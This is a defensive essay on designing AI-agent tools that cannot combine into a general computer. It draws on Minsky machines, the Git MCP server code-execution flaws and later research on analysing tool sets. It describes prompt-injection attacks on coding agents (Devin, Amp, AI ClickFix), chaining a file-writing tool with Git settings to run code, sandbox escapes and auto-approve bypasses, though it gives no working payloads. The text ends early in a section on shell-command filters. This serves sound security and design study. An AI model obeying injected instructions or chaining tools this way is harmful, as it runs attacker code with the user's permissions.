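# Designing tools for AI agents that cannot be combined into a general computer

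## What it means for tools to combine into a general computer

An AI agent is a language model that acts in a loop. It calls a tool, reads the result and chooses the next call, until it finishes the user's task or gives up. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to find mentions of an event in recent emails, summarize what happened and save the summary as a text file. The agent needs tools for searching the mailbox, fetching messages and writing to local storage, because a language model on its own only produces text, which changes nothing until another program acts on it.

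A tool is a function that the agent can call. The developer describes it to the model by a name, a short explanation and a schema, which declares the arguments the tool accepts and the type of each. A simplified description of a tool for setting reminders might look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "set_reminder",
  "description": "Remind the user of something on a given day.",
  "parameters": {
    "day":    { "type": "string", "format": "date" },
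    "repeat": { "type": "string", "enum": ["never", "weekly", "yearly"] },
    "text":   { "type": "string" }
  }
}
```

To use the tool, the model writes out a call:

```json
{
  "name": "set_reminder",
  "arguments": { "day": "2026-12-18", "repeat": "never", "text": "Renew passport" }
}
```

An ordinary program around the model reads the call, compares it with the schema, runs the function and adds the result to the text that the model reads next. The `repeat` argument is an enumerated value with three permitted choices, and the program can refuse anything else. The `day` argument can take many values, all of them dates. The `text` argument is a free-form string whose content the schema does not limit, so it could hold a shopping list or the source code of a program. This does no harm in a reminder as long as the text only ever appears on a screen for a person to read.

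The same string can do great harm if it reaches an interpreter, a program that treats its input as instructions. Shells, which carry out typed commands, and SQL engines, which carry out database queries, are both interpreters. Programs that read configuration files also count, because a line in such a file may name a command to run at start-up, but developers easily overlook them.

Developers must consider what an agent could do with its strings even when every user is honest, because of prompt injection. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (Natanzi and Tang, 2026) defines prompt injection as causing a model or application to treat attacker-controlled content as instructions. In the indirect form, the attacker plants the instructions in a web page, email, code repository or tool result that the agent later reads.

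Training models to ignore such text helps, but as Christodorescu and colleagues point out, agents often need to act on what they find. An agent summarizing one bug report may rightly notice that it depends on another and summarize both, and a tool's documentation is meant to change an agent's behavior. Trained refusals are also probabilistic, so if a model blocks unauthorized access 99% of the time, an attacker can target the remaining 1%. A limit built into a tool holds regardless of what the model has read or whether it makes a mistake.

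### Two harmless tools that can run any program

Suppose an agent has two tools. The first, `save_text(name, text)`, stores text in a work folder. The second, `run_job(name)`, starts a job from the same folder, and its developer meant it for routine jobs that colleagues wrote, such as a nightly backup.

An agent that has both `save_text` and `run_job` can save the source code of a new program and then run it, without a bug in either tool or a malformed argument. It can then do anything its permissions allow, such as reading passwords, deleting files or opening network connections. A reviewer who looks at each tool alone will not see this, because `save_text` by itself can only leave inert text behind and `run_job` by itself can only start programs that the staff put there. Using the effect or output of one tool as the input of another is called composition. Here it produces general computation,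 which is the power to make the environment run arbitrary programs with the agent's permissions.

Restricting the `name` argument of `run_job` to `backup`, `report` and `cleanup` with an enumerated type does not fix the problem if `save_text` can still overwrite the file called `backup`. Both tools use the same folder, which appears in neither schema, so inspecting the schemas alone would not reveal the problem.

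Real products have had the same flaw. Sourcegraph's coding agent Amp could edit its own settings file. Christodorescu and colleagues describe how a prompt injection could make it add malicious commands to the allow-list (the list of commands allowed to run automatically) or add an attacker's server to the configuration. Both led to unauthorized code running on the developer's machine. How much an agent can do by writing a settings file depends on which program reads the file afterwards. A Git tool and a file-writing tool also combined to run code in this way.

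### Two counters are enough to compute anything

A set of tools can combine into a general computer even if every tool accepts only fixed choices and no free-form strings, as a 65-year-old example shows.

The three tools `increment`, `decrement` and `is_zero` can combine into a general computer. Each takes one argument, `A` or `B`, which names one of two counters that hold whole numbers. In *Recursive Unsolvability of Post's Problem of "Tag"*, Minsky (1961) proved that these operations are enough to compute any function that any computer can compute. His programs use two forms of instruction. One adds 1 to a counter and moves to a specified next instruction. The other checks whether a counter is above zero. If it is, the instruction subtracts 1 and moves to one instruction; if not, it moves to a different one. In a Web of Stories interview recorded in 2011, *Solving Post's unsolvable problem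 leads to the 'Minsky Machines'*, Minsky described the result as a universal computer with two registers and four instructions, which add to or subtract from either register. Here, the tools hold the numbers, while the agent keeps track of its place in the program and chooses each call according to the last result from `is_zero`.

The construction starts from multiplication. To double the number in A, the agent subtracts 1 from A and adds 2 to B, and repeats this until A is empty. It then moves the contents of B back to A, 1 at a time. If A starts at 3, this takes 32 tool calls in total. Division works the same way in reverse, and the remainder shows whether the division was exact.

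Multiplication and division allow a single counter to store several numbers as exponents of different primes. For example, it can store *a* and *b* as 2<sup>*a*</sup> × 3<sup>*b*</sup>. Multiplying by 2 adds 1 to *a* and leaves *b* unchanged. Dividing by 3 subtracts 1 from *b*, and if 3 does not divide the number exactly, *b* must be zero. The other counter is scratch space for these operations.

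With this device Minsky could imitate a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer, which reads and writes symbols on a tape under the control of a finite set of rules. Read as a binary number, the symbols on the tape form an integer *k*. If the machine is looking at square *x*, the counter holds

2<sup>*k*</sup> × 3<sup>2<sup>*x*</sup></sup>.

To move one square to the right, Minsky's program doubles the exponent of 3 by replacing every factor of 3 with a 5, and then every 5 with a 9, which is 3 × 3. To write a 1 on a square that held a 0, it adds 2<sup>*x*</sup> to *k* by replacing every 3 with a 5, and then every 5 with a 6, which is 2 × 3. Reading a symbol takes a longer sequence of the same kind of replacements.

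Nobody would compute like this in practice. The theorem assumes counters of unlimited size and requires coded input. To work on the number *n*, the program must start with 2<sup>*n*</sup> in the first counter. For an input of 100, that is a 31-digit number, which the agent would have to count down one call at a time. But the theorem shows that, in principle, restricting each call to a short list of choices does not limit what a long sequence of calls can compute.

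The three tools are nevertheless safe because they can change only the values of two counters, however long the agent runs them and whatever it computes. By contrast, a tool called `delete_all_backups` that takes no arguments could ruin a company without computing anything.

The coding agent Devin is a less artificial case. It had a tool called `expose_port` that made a local program reachable from the internet for testing. In an attack that Christodorescu and colleagues recount, a web page with injected instructions led Devin to start a web server that served its entire file system, and then to make that server public with `expose_port`. Choosing a port takes only a number, but the tool became dangerous once the file server was listening on that port.

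A designer therefore needs to limit the agent's reach, the set of effects it can bring about with any sequence of tool calls. Trying to limit computation itself would be misguided and hopeless, because the model can supply it without any dangerous tool. In *Memory Augmented Large Language Models are Computationally Universal*, Schuurmans (2023) connected Google's model Flan-U-PaLM 540B to a simple external memory that stored named values, without changing the model's weights. A short program fetched each prompt from the memory, passed it to the model, and stored any assignments it found in the answer. Schuurmans then wrote a set of prompts that made this system imitate a universal Turing machine, one that can run any program, with 15 states and two symbols. The machine has at most 30 combinations of state and symbol, so the model's answer could be checked for each one. Without the memory,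 a deterministic model that reads text of bounded length is only a finite automaton, a machine with a fixed number of states that is strictly less powerful than a Turing machine.

The program around the model arguably did some of the computation in the earlier result. Schuurmans, Dai and Zanini (2024) accepted that this weakened the result, and removed the external memory in *Autoregressive Large Language Models are Computationally Universal*. They added the model's output to the end of a growing text while its attention window moved along from the beginning, and showed that a single system prompt could make gemini-1.5-pro-001 correctly apply all 2,027 rules of a universal system. This is a slightly unusual way to run a model, so the result does not carry over directly to every chatbot. The 2023 result matters more for tool design because almost any useful agent can store notes and read them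 back, which is all the memory the argument requires.

### The path from the model's text to an interpreter

If computation is harmless in the counters but dangerous in the work folder, the danger must depend on where the computation runs. An agent's tools give it a general computer when text the model controls can become input to an interpreter that can run arbitrary programs with the agent's permissions.

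Such a path usually starts with a free-form string, but an agent can also build up text from small pieces. For example, a tool called `append_character` takes only an enumerated value, one of a hundred permitted characters, and adds it to a file. An agent can write a 5,000-character program by calling it 5,000 times. As with the counters, the designer has to consider what accumulates over many calls as well as what fits into one.

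The path can run through any place that stores or carries text. In AI ClickFix, an attack that Christodorescu and colleagues include among their cases, a web page instructed an agent to click a button that secretly copied a command to the clipboard, then to open a terminal and paste it. The agent only had to move the attacker's command from one place to another. In another of their cases, Terminal DiLLMa, the path ended in the terminal program that displayed the assistant's output. Terminal programs treat certain invisible character sequences as instructions, so a command-line assistant that printed its answer unfiltered could manipulate the user's clipboard or leak data through network lookups.

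In principle, a designer can search for such paths before deployment by listing every place the tools can write to and every place an interpreter reads from, then looking for overlap. The second list is harder to make because it has to include files that programs read automatically. It also goes out of date whenever somebody installs new software or adds a tool, so a safe set of tools can become unsafe even if none of the original tools changes.

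The path condition also does not cover every harm. An agent that can send email can send a private document to the wrong person without any interpreter. But closing the paths to interpreters removes the largest and least predictable part of what an agent can do, and leaves a list of effects that a person can at least read and judge.

### Five design rules

Five rules follow for the design of tool interfaces.

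- Narrow types: give each argument the tightest type that the task allows, such as a date, a whole number from 1 to 50, or an identifier that the system itself issued.
- Enumerated values: where only a few choices are useful, list them and refuse the rest. An injected instruction can then do no more than pick among options that the developer has already considered.
- Outputs that no other tool interprets: keep whatever a tool writes out of every place from which an interpreter reads. In the example above, `save_text` and `run_job` would use separate folders, and `save_text` could not reach the folder with the jobs.
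- Checks on arguments: where a string has to remain, let ordinary code test it before the tool acts, preferably against an allow-list. The code might confirm, for instance, that a file lies inside the project folder.
- Parameterized queries: fix the structure of a database query first and fill in the values afterwards, so that the database engine never reads a value as part of a command.

These rules remove or guard the path. Another approach leaves the path open but runs the interpreter in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what running code can access.

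Natanzi and Tang list weak schemas among the typical vulnerabilities of tool-using agents, and structured tool interfaces among the defenses. They classify the literature but don't measure how well the defenses work. How much each rule protects, and how much it reduces utility (the share of legitimate tasks that the agent completes), depends on the tools.

### Where the rules come from

The principle of least privilege, which security engineers have taught since the 1970s, holds that every program and user should have only the privileges the job requires. Restricting the values an argument can take applies this principle to a single function call.

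Least privilege does not specify how to handle a program that needs broad powers for one purpose and must not use them for another. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes such a program, a compiler at the timesharing company Tymshare. The compiler had permission to write in its own directory so that it could store usage statistics there. Users could also give it the name of a file to receive debugging output. One user gave it the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, it overwrote the billing information with debugging output.

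The file name was a free-form string, and Hardy's reasons why the company could not simply check it still apply to agents. Banning other directories would have blocked legitimate uses. The programmers could not ban that particular directory because its name did not exist when they wrote the code. Banning the billing file would have left every other sensitive file exposed. Each new exception made the rules more complex, until the conditions for opening a file contained fourteen logical operators.

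Hardy traced the fault to the compiler's two sources of authority, its own license and the user's, which it could not keep apart. Hardy favored using capabilities, objects that both identify a file and grant permission to use it. Users could then hand over only files they already had the right to write to, and the compiler would not need file names. An agent under prompt injection is in much the same position as the compiler, because it holds the user's permissions while acting on a stranger's text.

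The no-execute bit in processors is a hardware counterpart to the rule about outputs. It marks a region of memory as data, and the processor will not run anything stored there. To show that agents lack an equally reliable safeguard, Christodorescu and colleagues ask whether anyone could build a defense on a no-execute bit that worked only with some probability.

The closest ancestor of the path condition is language-theoretic security (LANGSEC), a research program from around 2011. According to LANGSEC's home page, *The Tower of Babel*, software that accepts untrusted input should define the valid inputs as a formal language, with exact rules for what belongs to it, and test every input against those rules. For sufficiently complex languages the test is undecidable, meaning no procedure can always give the right answer, so no amount of checking will make the software secure. This limits what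 the rule about checking arguments can achieve. A check can be complete when the argument is a date or a file name in a known folder, but no check can decide in general what a program passed as an argument will do. The slides of *Stopping 0 Days with Formal Languages* relate this to least privilege, describing any extra computational power that a program exposes to its input as privilege given to the attacker.

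The same researchers popularized the term "weird machine". Sassaman, Bratus and Patterson (2011) use it for a programmable environment, more powerful than its designers intended, that arises when crafted input puts a program into an unexpected state. An exploit is then a program for that machine. In the same year, Bratus, Locasto and colleagues, in *Exploit Programming*, called for combining hackers' skill at finding such machines with the theory of computation. Together, `save_text` and `run_job` fit the description, except that the classic weird machine depends on a failure, such as corrupted memory. These two tools work exactly as specified, so fixing bugs will not remove the machine they form.

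The preference for narrow arguments also has a precedent in the design of the web. In *The Rule of Least Power*, Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn (2006) advised publishers to use the least powerful language suitable for the purpose. Their main concern was reuse, because anyone can analyze a table of weather data, but usually the only way to learn what an arbitrary program will do is to run it. They added that less powerful languages are usually easier to secure. They also warned that a language too limited for its task leads people to clumsy workarounds, which bring back the complexity the restriction was meant to avoid. Tool designers face the same risk, because an agent whose tools are too narrow will fail at legitimate tasks, and its developers will be tempted to give it a shell.

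## A Git tool and a file-writing tool that together ran code

Anthropic introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP) in November 2024. It is an open standard for connecting AI applications to servers, which are programs that each offer an agent a set of tools. One of Anthropic's own servers, `mcp-server-git`, lets an agent work with Git, the program most developers use to record versions of their code. It was a reference implementation, meant to show other developers how to give agents safe access to repositories, the project folders that Git tracks (SiliconANGLE, 2026).

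In 2025 the security company Cyata found three flaws in this server. According to Cyata's *How We Found Code Execution in Anthropic’s Official Git MCP Server*, they could be exploited in any configuration, and an attacker only had to influence something the agent would read, such as a project's README file or an issue description. The flaws alone let an attacker use prompt injection to read or destroy files. If the agent also had a tool that could write files, the attacker could run code on the developer's machine.

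### Three design faults

The flaws are CVE-2025-68143 through CVE-2025-68145 in the CVE catalog, a public list of software flaws that the nonprofit MITRE maintains. Each is a fault in the design of a tool's interface.

The `git_init` tool turned a folder into a repository, and it accepted any path. MITRE's *mcp-server-git's unrestricted git_init tool allows repository creation at arbitrary filesystem locations* (2025) points out that the server's other tools needed an existing repository. An agent could therefore use `git_init` to give those tools access to any folder within the server's permissions, and private files in that folder could end up in the text that the model reads.

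The Git server never checked tool calls against its configured path limit. A developer could start it with a setting meant to confine it to one repository, but each tool call also carried a free-form string called `repo_path`, and the server used whatever path it contained. Calls could therefore operate on any other repository the server had permission to access, according to MITRE's *mcp-server-git has missing path validation when using --repository flag* (2025).

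The `git_diff` tool shows how versions of a project differ. Its `target` argument, another free-form string, was meant to name a version to compare. The server passed the string to Git's command line, and Git treats a word that begins with a hyphen as an option, which changes what the command does. One such option sends the output to a file, so a tool for viewing changes could overwrite any file the server had permission to write. The `git_checkout` tool, which switches between versions, had the same fault, according to MITRE's entry for CVE-2025-68144 (2025).

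### How a settings file became a command

None of these faults lets an agent run a program of its own. The Git server had no tool for writing arbitrary text, and Anthropic's separate server for file operations could write text but had no tool for starting programs. Cyata found that most coding environments at the time gave the agent either that file server or a built-in way to write files.

The two tools could be combined to run code because Git takes instructions from files. Each repository has a plain-text settings file, which can name a command for Git to run during routine operations. An agent could use `git_init` to create a repository in a folder where the file-writing tool could also write, then use that tool to change the repository's settings. An ordinary Git operation would then run the attacker's command with the developer's permissions.

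Operating systems run a file as a program only if it has execute permission, which the file-writing tools never granted. Cyata's researchers therefore had to abandon their first idea, a Git feature that depends on this permission. The settings file doesn't need execute permission, because Git reads the file as data and then passes the commands it contains to a shell.

This kind of fault might be called re-interpreted output. One tool writes text that does nothing by itself, and another program later reads it as instructions, so the model's text reaches an interpreter. Some sandboxes don't prevent this. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) describes escapes reproduced across four coding agents. In nearly all of them, the agent only had to write something that a trusted program outside the sandbox would later run, load or treat as safe.

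A reviewer who examined each tool separately would have had little reason to expect code execution. `git_init` creates a few bookkeeping files and doesn't start any programs. The file server is meant to write text in folders the developer has opened to it. The CVE catalog also scores each flaw separately. MITRE lists the three flaws at 6.5, 6.4 and 6.3 out of 10, all medium severity, and code execution appears in none of their descriptions. TechRadar's *Anthropic's official Git MCP server had some worrying security flaws* quotes Cyata as saying that each server "might look safe in isolation" but that the two together make "a toxic combination".

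The reporting process took almost six months. Cyata sent its first report on June 24, 2025, through HackerOne, a service that passes security reports to companies. The report covered the unchecked path and the reading of private files. A day later it was marked "informative", HackerOne's status for reports that call for no immediate fix. Cyata's researchers kept looking for a more direct impact, and on July 6 they sent a second report covering the option fault and the code execution. Anthropic reopened the case on July 24 and accepted it on September 10. The three CVE numbers and the last fix followed on December 17, and Cyata published its account on January 20, 2026. The CVE entry for `git_init` lists 2025.9.25 as the repaired version. The entries for the other two faults list 2025.12.17, but Cyata gives 2025.12.18, as does GitLab's *CVE-2025-68145* (2025), which was updated three days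 after the fix. TechRadar reported no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaws.

### What the repairs cost a developer

Anthropic fixed each fault separately. It removed `git_init` because the server should only work with existing repositories. To enforce the path limit, the server now resolves both the configured path and the requested one, following symbolic links (entries that point to another location), and refuses the call unless the requested path lies inside the configured one. The server also rejects values for the text argument that begin with a hyphen, then uses Git to check that the value refers to a real version, as MITRE describes.

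These repairs cause little inconvenience. The developer can start a new repository by hand with one command. Somebody who works on several repositories has to configure access to each. An agent can use one of Git's many display options only if the server offers it as a separate argument, as it already did for the number of lines of context to show.

The repairs limit how the two servers can be combined to run code, but they don't necessarily prevent it. If the file-writing tool can write inside the configured repository, it can also change the settings that Git follows there. Preventing this requires making the file-writing tool block those changes.

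The cleanest change is to keep the file tool from writing in any folder where Git operates. This barely limits an agent that writes reports in one folder and consults a repository in another, but it would not work for a coding agent, whose job is to edit the files that Git tracks.

A coding agent can still do its work if the file tool blocks writes only to the files that control what Git does. The developer must then identify those files, and do the same for the editor, the package manager and every other program that reads the project folder. If the agent is also allowed to run the project's tests, it has access to an interpreter by design, and no list of protected files will remove that access.

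Protecting configuration files also blocks some changes that users want. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) replayed a session in which a developer asked an agent to add instructions to `.bashrc`, a file of commands that the shell runs when it starts. A sandbox with one fixed policy for all sessions blocked the change because writes to such files are usually suspicious. The developer would have had to edit the file by hand or loosen the policy for every session.

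Guarding files doesn't have to make an agent less useful. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) reports that YoloFS, a file system for coding agents, matched the baseline's success rate on 112 routine tasks with fewer user interactions. Routine tasks are the favorable case, though, because few of them touch a start-up file.

### Following the paths through a whole tool set

Cyata advises developers to audit which servers run together. For a modest number of tools, a reviewer can do this on paper by listing every place each tool can write to and every place it takes instructions from. A place can be a folder, a database, the clipboard or a shared variable. The reviewer also notes which tools carry content from one place to another.

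The reviewer then lists every place where a tool can put text that the model chooses. This text can include anything the model has read, because a model can copy an attacker's words into any free-form string. Next, the reviewer adds each place that some tool can fill from a place already on the list, and repeats this step until a full round adds nothing. The search always ends because the number of places is finite and none is removed from the list. If the final list includes a place from which an interpreter takes instructions, there is a path.

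Suppose a local history society has an agent with five tools. Staff edit the pages in the `site` folder by hand, and `build_site` turns them into a website. The program that `build_site` runs also reads `site/settings`, which can specify a command to run before the build.

| Tool | Writes to | Takes instructions from |
|---|---|---|
| `read_mail()` | nothing | nothing |
| `save_note(name, text)` | `notes` | nothing |
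| `add_event(date, title)` | the calendar | nothing |
| `draw_chart(table)` | `charts` | nothing |
| `build_site()` | `public` | `site/settings` |

The model can write its own text to `notes` and the calendar. The charts come from tables that the staff maintain, and the website comes from `site`. No tool moves anything out of `notes` or the calendar, so the search stops after one round with two places on the list, neither of which is `site/settings`. A malicious email might still lead the model to fill the calendar with nonsense, but it cannot make the model run a program.

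The society then adds a sixth tool, `move_file(file, folder)`, so that the agent can tidy up. The tool seems to follow the rules for narrow arguments well. Both arguments are enumerated values, so the agent can only pick an existing file and one of the four folders, and the tool accepts no text and starts no program. But the agent can use it to move a note into `site`. If the agent has named the note `settings`, it replaces the staff's file, and the next call to `build_site` runs whatever command the note contains.

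This path needs all three tools: `save_note` cannot reach `site`, `move_file` cannot write new text, and `build_site` cannot change its own settings. A reviewer who compared the tools two at a time would miss the path, but the search finds it in its first round.

The society can block the path at any step. It could drop `site` from the folders that `move_file` offers, but then staff would have to copy a note over themselves to publish it as a page. It could make `save_note` add `.txt` to every name, which has almost no downside but stops working if a later version of the site builder takes commands from other files. Or it could keep the settings in a folder that none of the tools can reach. This takes some one-time work, but the agent can still do everything it could before.

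In the Git case, the search would have taken a minute if the reviewer had put Git's settings file in the right-hand column. Knowing to put it there was difficult. Cyata's researchers suspected that something was there, but they still had to go through Git's features to find one that would run a command. A reviewer with less time might be wise to assume that any program of Git's size takes instructions from files in the folder where it works, until someone shows otherwise.

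### Deriving the graph from code

Since tool descriptions leave out much of what matters, researchers have begun to build these lists from the tools' source code. In *ACaM* (November 2026), Santra, Kirat and colleagues presented a system that does this for agents written in Python. In their running example, `get_news` fetches headlines and stores its access token for the news service in a variable that all the tools share. `sync_prefs` then sends the contents of this variable to a server that holds the user's preferences. Each tool roughly matches its description, but together they send the token to a server that doesn't need it.

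ACaM builds a graph of the agent's tools and the channels between them, such as files, shared variables, databases and network calls. It labels each channel as public, internal or secret, and traces the data by static analysis, which examines code without running it. It then uses a language model only for questions that the structure of the code cannot settle. For instance, static analysis cannot distinguish a branch that depends on a user's role, which probably guards a privilege, from one that depends on the user's language, which does not. The model cannot override what static analysis has established.

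When the answer for one tool depends on another tool, ACaM records a condition, such as "`sync_prefs` leaks a secret only if `get_news` has put one into the shared variable." It then goes through the graph repeatedly, resolving these conditions until a full pass changes nothing, much like the search by hand.

The researchers tested ACaM on 43 real agents with about six tools each. They worked out the right answers by hand for 24 cases: ten of the original agents and 14 variants with planted leaks. ACaM's F1 score, which falls when a system reports capabilities that don't exist or misses ones that do, was 98.3%. Static analysis alone scored 93.4%. Language models alone scored 81.4%, even when the researchers picked the best of twelve set-ups for each agent.

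ACaM also had to reconstruct the planted leaks from end to end, and scored 0.980 out of 1. The best result for language models alone was 0.903, and conventional code scanners got no higher than 0.342, since they don't account for a model that decides which tool runs next. The language models were good at identifying the secret and the place where it left the system, but they failed to give the full sequence of steps in 40% of cases, against 7% for ACaM. A chatbot asked whether a tool set is safe may therefore miss the sequence, which a review of single tools also misses.

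ACaM found 107 distinct paths to code execution and 16 that exposed credentials in the 43 unmodified agents, and the researchers confirmed by hand that all 123 exist in the code. They built working attacks for ten of the findings, including some less severe ones, and six of these attacks ran arbitrary code. In one of the six, one component saved a file the model had written and another ran it, as with `save_text` and `run_job`. All ten attacks worked against a small model with little safety training. Claude Haiku 4.5 blocked the bluntly worded versions, but all ten succeeded when the researchers worded the prompts more subtly. They did not try larger models. Two of the attacks needed no decision by a model, because the agent ran code from a tampered data file as it started up.

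The analysis costs about 77 cents and takes about a minute per agent. ACaM's main gaps involve remote services, whose code it cannot analyze, and file paths that a program assembles while running. It cannot determine which file such a path names, so it may miss a leak. Otherwise, it tends to produce false alarms. It assumes that the model may call any tools in any order, and it never counts a check on an argument as making the data safe, so it still reports a data path after a developer has repaired it with a good check.

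Adam and colleagues, at Brown University, try to avoid such false alarms by adding a second stage. Static analysis first lists the effects a tool's code can have, such as writing files or opening network connections. Where an effect is sometimes acceptable, the tool's developer wraps only that operation in a small sandbox. The program around the model sends the sandbox a policy with each call, and the sandbox checks the actual file path or web address against it. A second analysis verifies that the developer has wrapped every such operation and has not tampered with the policy before it reaches the sandbox.

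The researchers compared four protections in three scenarios. Each scenario had a harmless version that the user wanted and a version that went wrong. In one, the agent copies a settings file into a project and later publishes the project on GitHub. This is harmless if the file holds only debugging options, but it leaks any secret key in the file. The researchers had seen Claude 4.5 Haiku leak a key this way.

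| Protection | Wanted versions allowed | Unwanted versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox with a fixed policy | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| List of effects alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| List of effects with a small sandbox in each tool | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

The fixed policy could not distinguish a harmless settings file from one containing a key, so it let both out. The list of effects alone stopped every leak, but it also blocked a file the user wanted, because nothing in the code guaranteed where the file would go. With only three scenarios, the test is more a demonstration than a measurement. The researchers also supplied the right policy for each call, which is arguably the hardest part of the problem. The analysis covers only the tool's own language, here Rust. When a tool passes text to a shell, a database or a web service, the analysis has to assume the worst,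 and these are the places where re-interpreted output does damage.

### Showing a risky tool only when a task needs it

A different way to break up dangerous combinations is to hide tools. An agent that summarizes an email doesn't need tools for sending or deleting mail, and if it cannot call them, injected text cannot make it send or delete anything. In *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, Iyer and Babu (2026) turn this into a rule that a program applies before each step.

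Each tool carries a description of the facts it needs and the facts it produces, along with a risk level. Sending email is high-risk, for example, and requires the fact that somebody has confirmed the recipient. The program looks for the best sequence of tools that leads from the present facts to the goal, by minimizing

total cost of the tools + *λ* × total risk of the tools,

where each tool costs 1, and low, medium and high risk count as 0, 1 and 4. It then shows the agent only the next tool in this sequence, and withholds a risky one until its authorization is in place. At the recommended setting of *λ* = 2, one high-risk tool adds 8 to the total, so the program will accept up to seven extra steps to avoid it.

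To test the rule, Iyer and Babu used a simulated agent that obeyed every injected instruction if it could see the tool the instruction required. With all tools visible, the attack success rate was 100%. Showing only the tools that the task needed next, without regard to risk, reduced the rate to 25%, and applying the full rule reduced it to zero. The agent completed every legitimate task in all three conditions. Tests with seven real language models produced the same attack success rates of 25% and zero, and the models used about 17% more text per task under the full rule because of the added confirmation steps. With *λ* set to 0.5, however, the program kept choosing shortcuts through risky tools that it then had to withhold, and the agent completed only 89% of tasks.

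The design almost guarantees the attack success rate of zero, since an agent cannot call a tool it does not have. But the result depends on attackers being unable to forge the authorization. When Iyer and Babu let injected text mark a recipient as confirmed, the rate went back to 25%. That figure reflects their test design, in which 20 of the 80 tasks under attack offered a dangerous shortcut.

The current rule would do little about tools that are dangerous only in combination. Iyer and Babu assign risk to single tools, and acknowledge that a tool can be benign alone but dangerous in a sequence. `save_note` and `move_file` would hardly be labeled high-risk. A path search could produce better labels by flagging every tool on a path to an interpreter. But hiding a tool does not remove what it has already written. A settings file from an earlier step is still there when the tool that reads it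 becomes visible, even if the agent never sees both tools at once.

### How often servers fail to enforce their own limits

All of these methods assume that a tool's limits hold. If a tool can write outside its folder, the list of places it can write to is wrong, and conclusions drawn from that list are unreliable. *ToFu* (Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues, October 2026) tested this assumption on open-source MCP servers and found 253 flaws across 118 of the 273 servers it could properly run.

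ToFu is a fuzzer, a program that feeds software large numbers of unusual inputs to see what goes wrong. Ordinary fuzzers look for crashes, but a tool that reads a password file outside its workspace returns a normal result without crashing. ToFu therefore bases its tests on the description the tool gives to agents. If an argument's description is "a file within the workspace", ToFu tries paths that lead outside and checks which file the tool opens. A language model picks suitable tests from a library of 74 and drafts the starting inputs, but fixed code decides whether a tool has failed.

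The fuzzer flagged 508 candidates. The researchers reviewed them all by hand, threw out 103 that were not real vulnerabilities, and merged 152 duplicates. The remaining 253 flaws affect 343 tools, since several tools can share one. In 64 cases a tool accepted a path outside its permitted folder, the same class of fault as the unchecked limit in Anthropic's Git server. Seven made a server fetch web addresses it should have refused, five leaked data, three allowed commands to run, and one left a temporary file behind.

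The other 173 flaws, about two thirds of the total, are milder. In 115 cases, a tool returned hostile text without neutralizing the characters that a program such as a browser might treat as instructions. In 58 cases, an input could plant false entries in a log. These flaws do no damage until something else reads the text, but they are the ones that lead to re-interpreted output. How serious they are depends on which other tools and programs are present, and a test of a single server cannot show that.

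The count is incomplete. The researchers started from 1,404 servers that offered at least one tool, but most of these would not build or needed accounts and databases that were not available. Even on the 273 servers, only about 1,500 of the 3,405 tools ran in a typical round of tests. Roughly three quarters to four fifths of the flaws were the same in two rounds with identical settings, so a further round would probably turn up more. ToFu also tests each tool separately. It might have caught the missing path check in the Git server, but it cannot discover that a second server could write Git's settings. Ananto and colleagues leave sequences of calls to future work and describe how to choose useful sequences in a large collection of tools as an open problem.

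Running the tools seems to produce fewer false alarms than scanning their code alone. Manual review confirmed about 80% of ToFu's candidates, counting duplicates. In *Hunt Them All*, Oliveira and Fiser used AI to scan the code of more than 19,000 server repositories, and found that only 4.1% of the vulnerabilities it identified were exploitable. The two figures measure somewhat different things, since a flaw can be real without being exploitable. But a developer who relies on a code scan alone should expect to spend much of the time on false alarms. Running the tools is also risky. During the tests, four of the servers affected the researchers' own machine, and one of them deleted files outside its workspace.

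## Checking the arguments of shell commands in coding agents

Most coding agents have a tool that passes one free-form string to a shell. This tool can search files, install a library, run the tests or commit a change to Git. Its schema limits almost nothing, so any restriction has to come from a separate check on the string.

Approving every command is tedious for developers, so many products run some commands without asking. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, does this for a built-in set that includes `ls` (which lists files), `grep` (which searches text) and the read-only forms of Git commands. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes a similar arrangement for the company's coding agent, Codex, in which common benign commands are allowed and certain dangerous ones are blocked or need approval.

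### Why harmless commands are hard to recognize

A shell rewrites the text of a command before running it. It removes quotation marks, replaces variables with their values, and runs any nested commands, inserting their output. A checker that tests the original text is therefore testing something other than what will run. `cat notes.txt` and `cat "notes.txt"` are different strings, but the shell does the same thing with both. A string that the checker reads as one permitted program can also make the shell run a second program. VulnCheck's *Roo-Code 3.54.0 Auto-Approve Bypass via Shell Parser Word-Boundary Mismatch*, an advisory on the coding agent Roo Code, labels this an "interpretation conflict", a term used in security catalogs.

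Even a checker that parsed the text exactly as the shell does would have trouble with options. The program `find` usually lists files, but it also has options that delete them, write to a file or start another program. *Prompt injection to RCE in AI agents* (2025) reports that the security company Trail of Bits ran code of its choice on three popular agents through pre-approved commands. Blocking all options would make these programs useless, and blocking only the dangerous ones requires knowing every option of every program on the list, which can run to hundreds.

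Some commands are risky even without unusual options. Roo Code's default list of commands to run without asking once included `npm install`, which installs JavaScript packages. This command also runs scripts that come with the project, as OSV's *CVE-2025-58374* (2025) explains. Analyzing the command's text would not have helped, because the list was meant to allow that command.

### Matching patterns on the raw text

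The simplest checker compares the command with a list of patterns. With a block-list, the checker stops any command that matches and passes the rest to the shell. With an allow-list, it passes only commands that match. In both cases, the shell rewrites the command string after the checker has approved it.

Adversa AI's *GuardFall*, a survey from June 30, 2026, shows that this works badly. The security company examined eleven popular open-source agents. It found each agent's filter in its source code and tested it with commands that use shell features covered in security textbooks for decades. It then ran the agents with Claude Sonnet 4.6 in an isolated home folder, planted instructions in material such as README files, and checked whether a marker file had changed.

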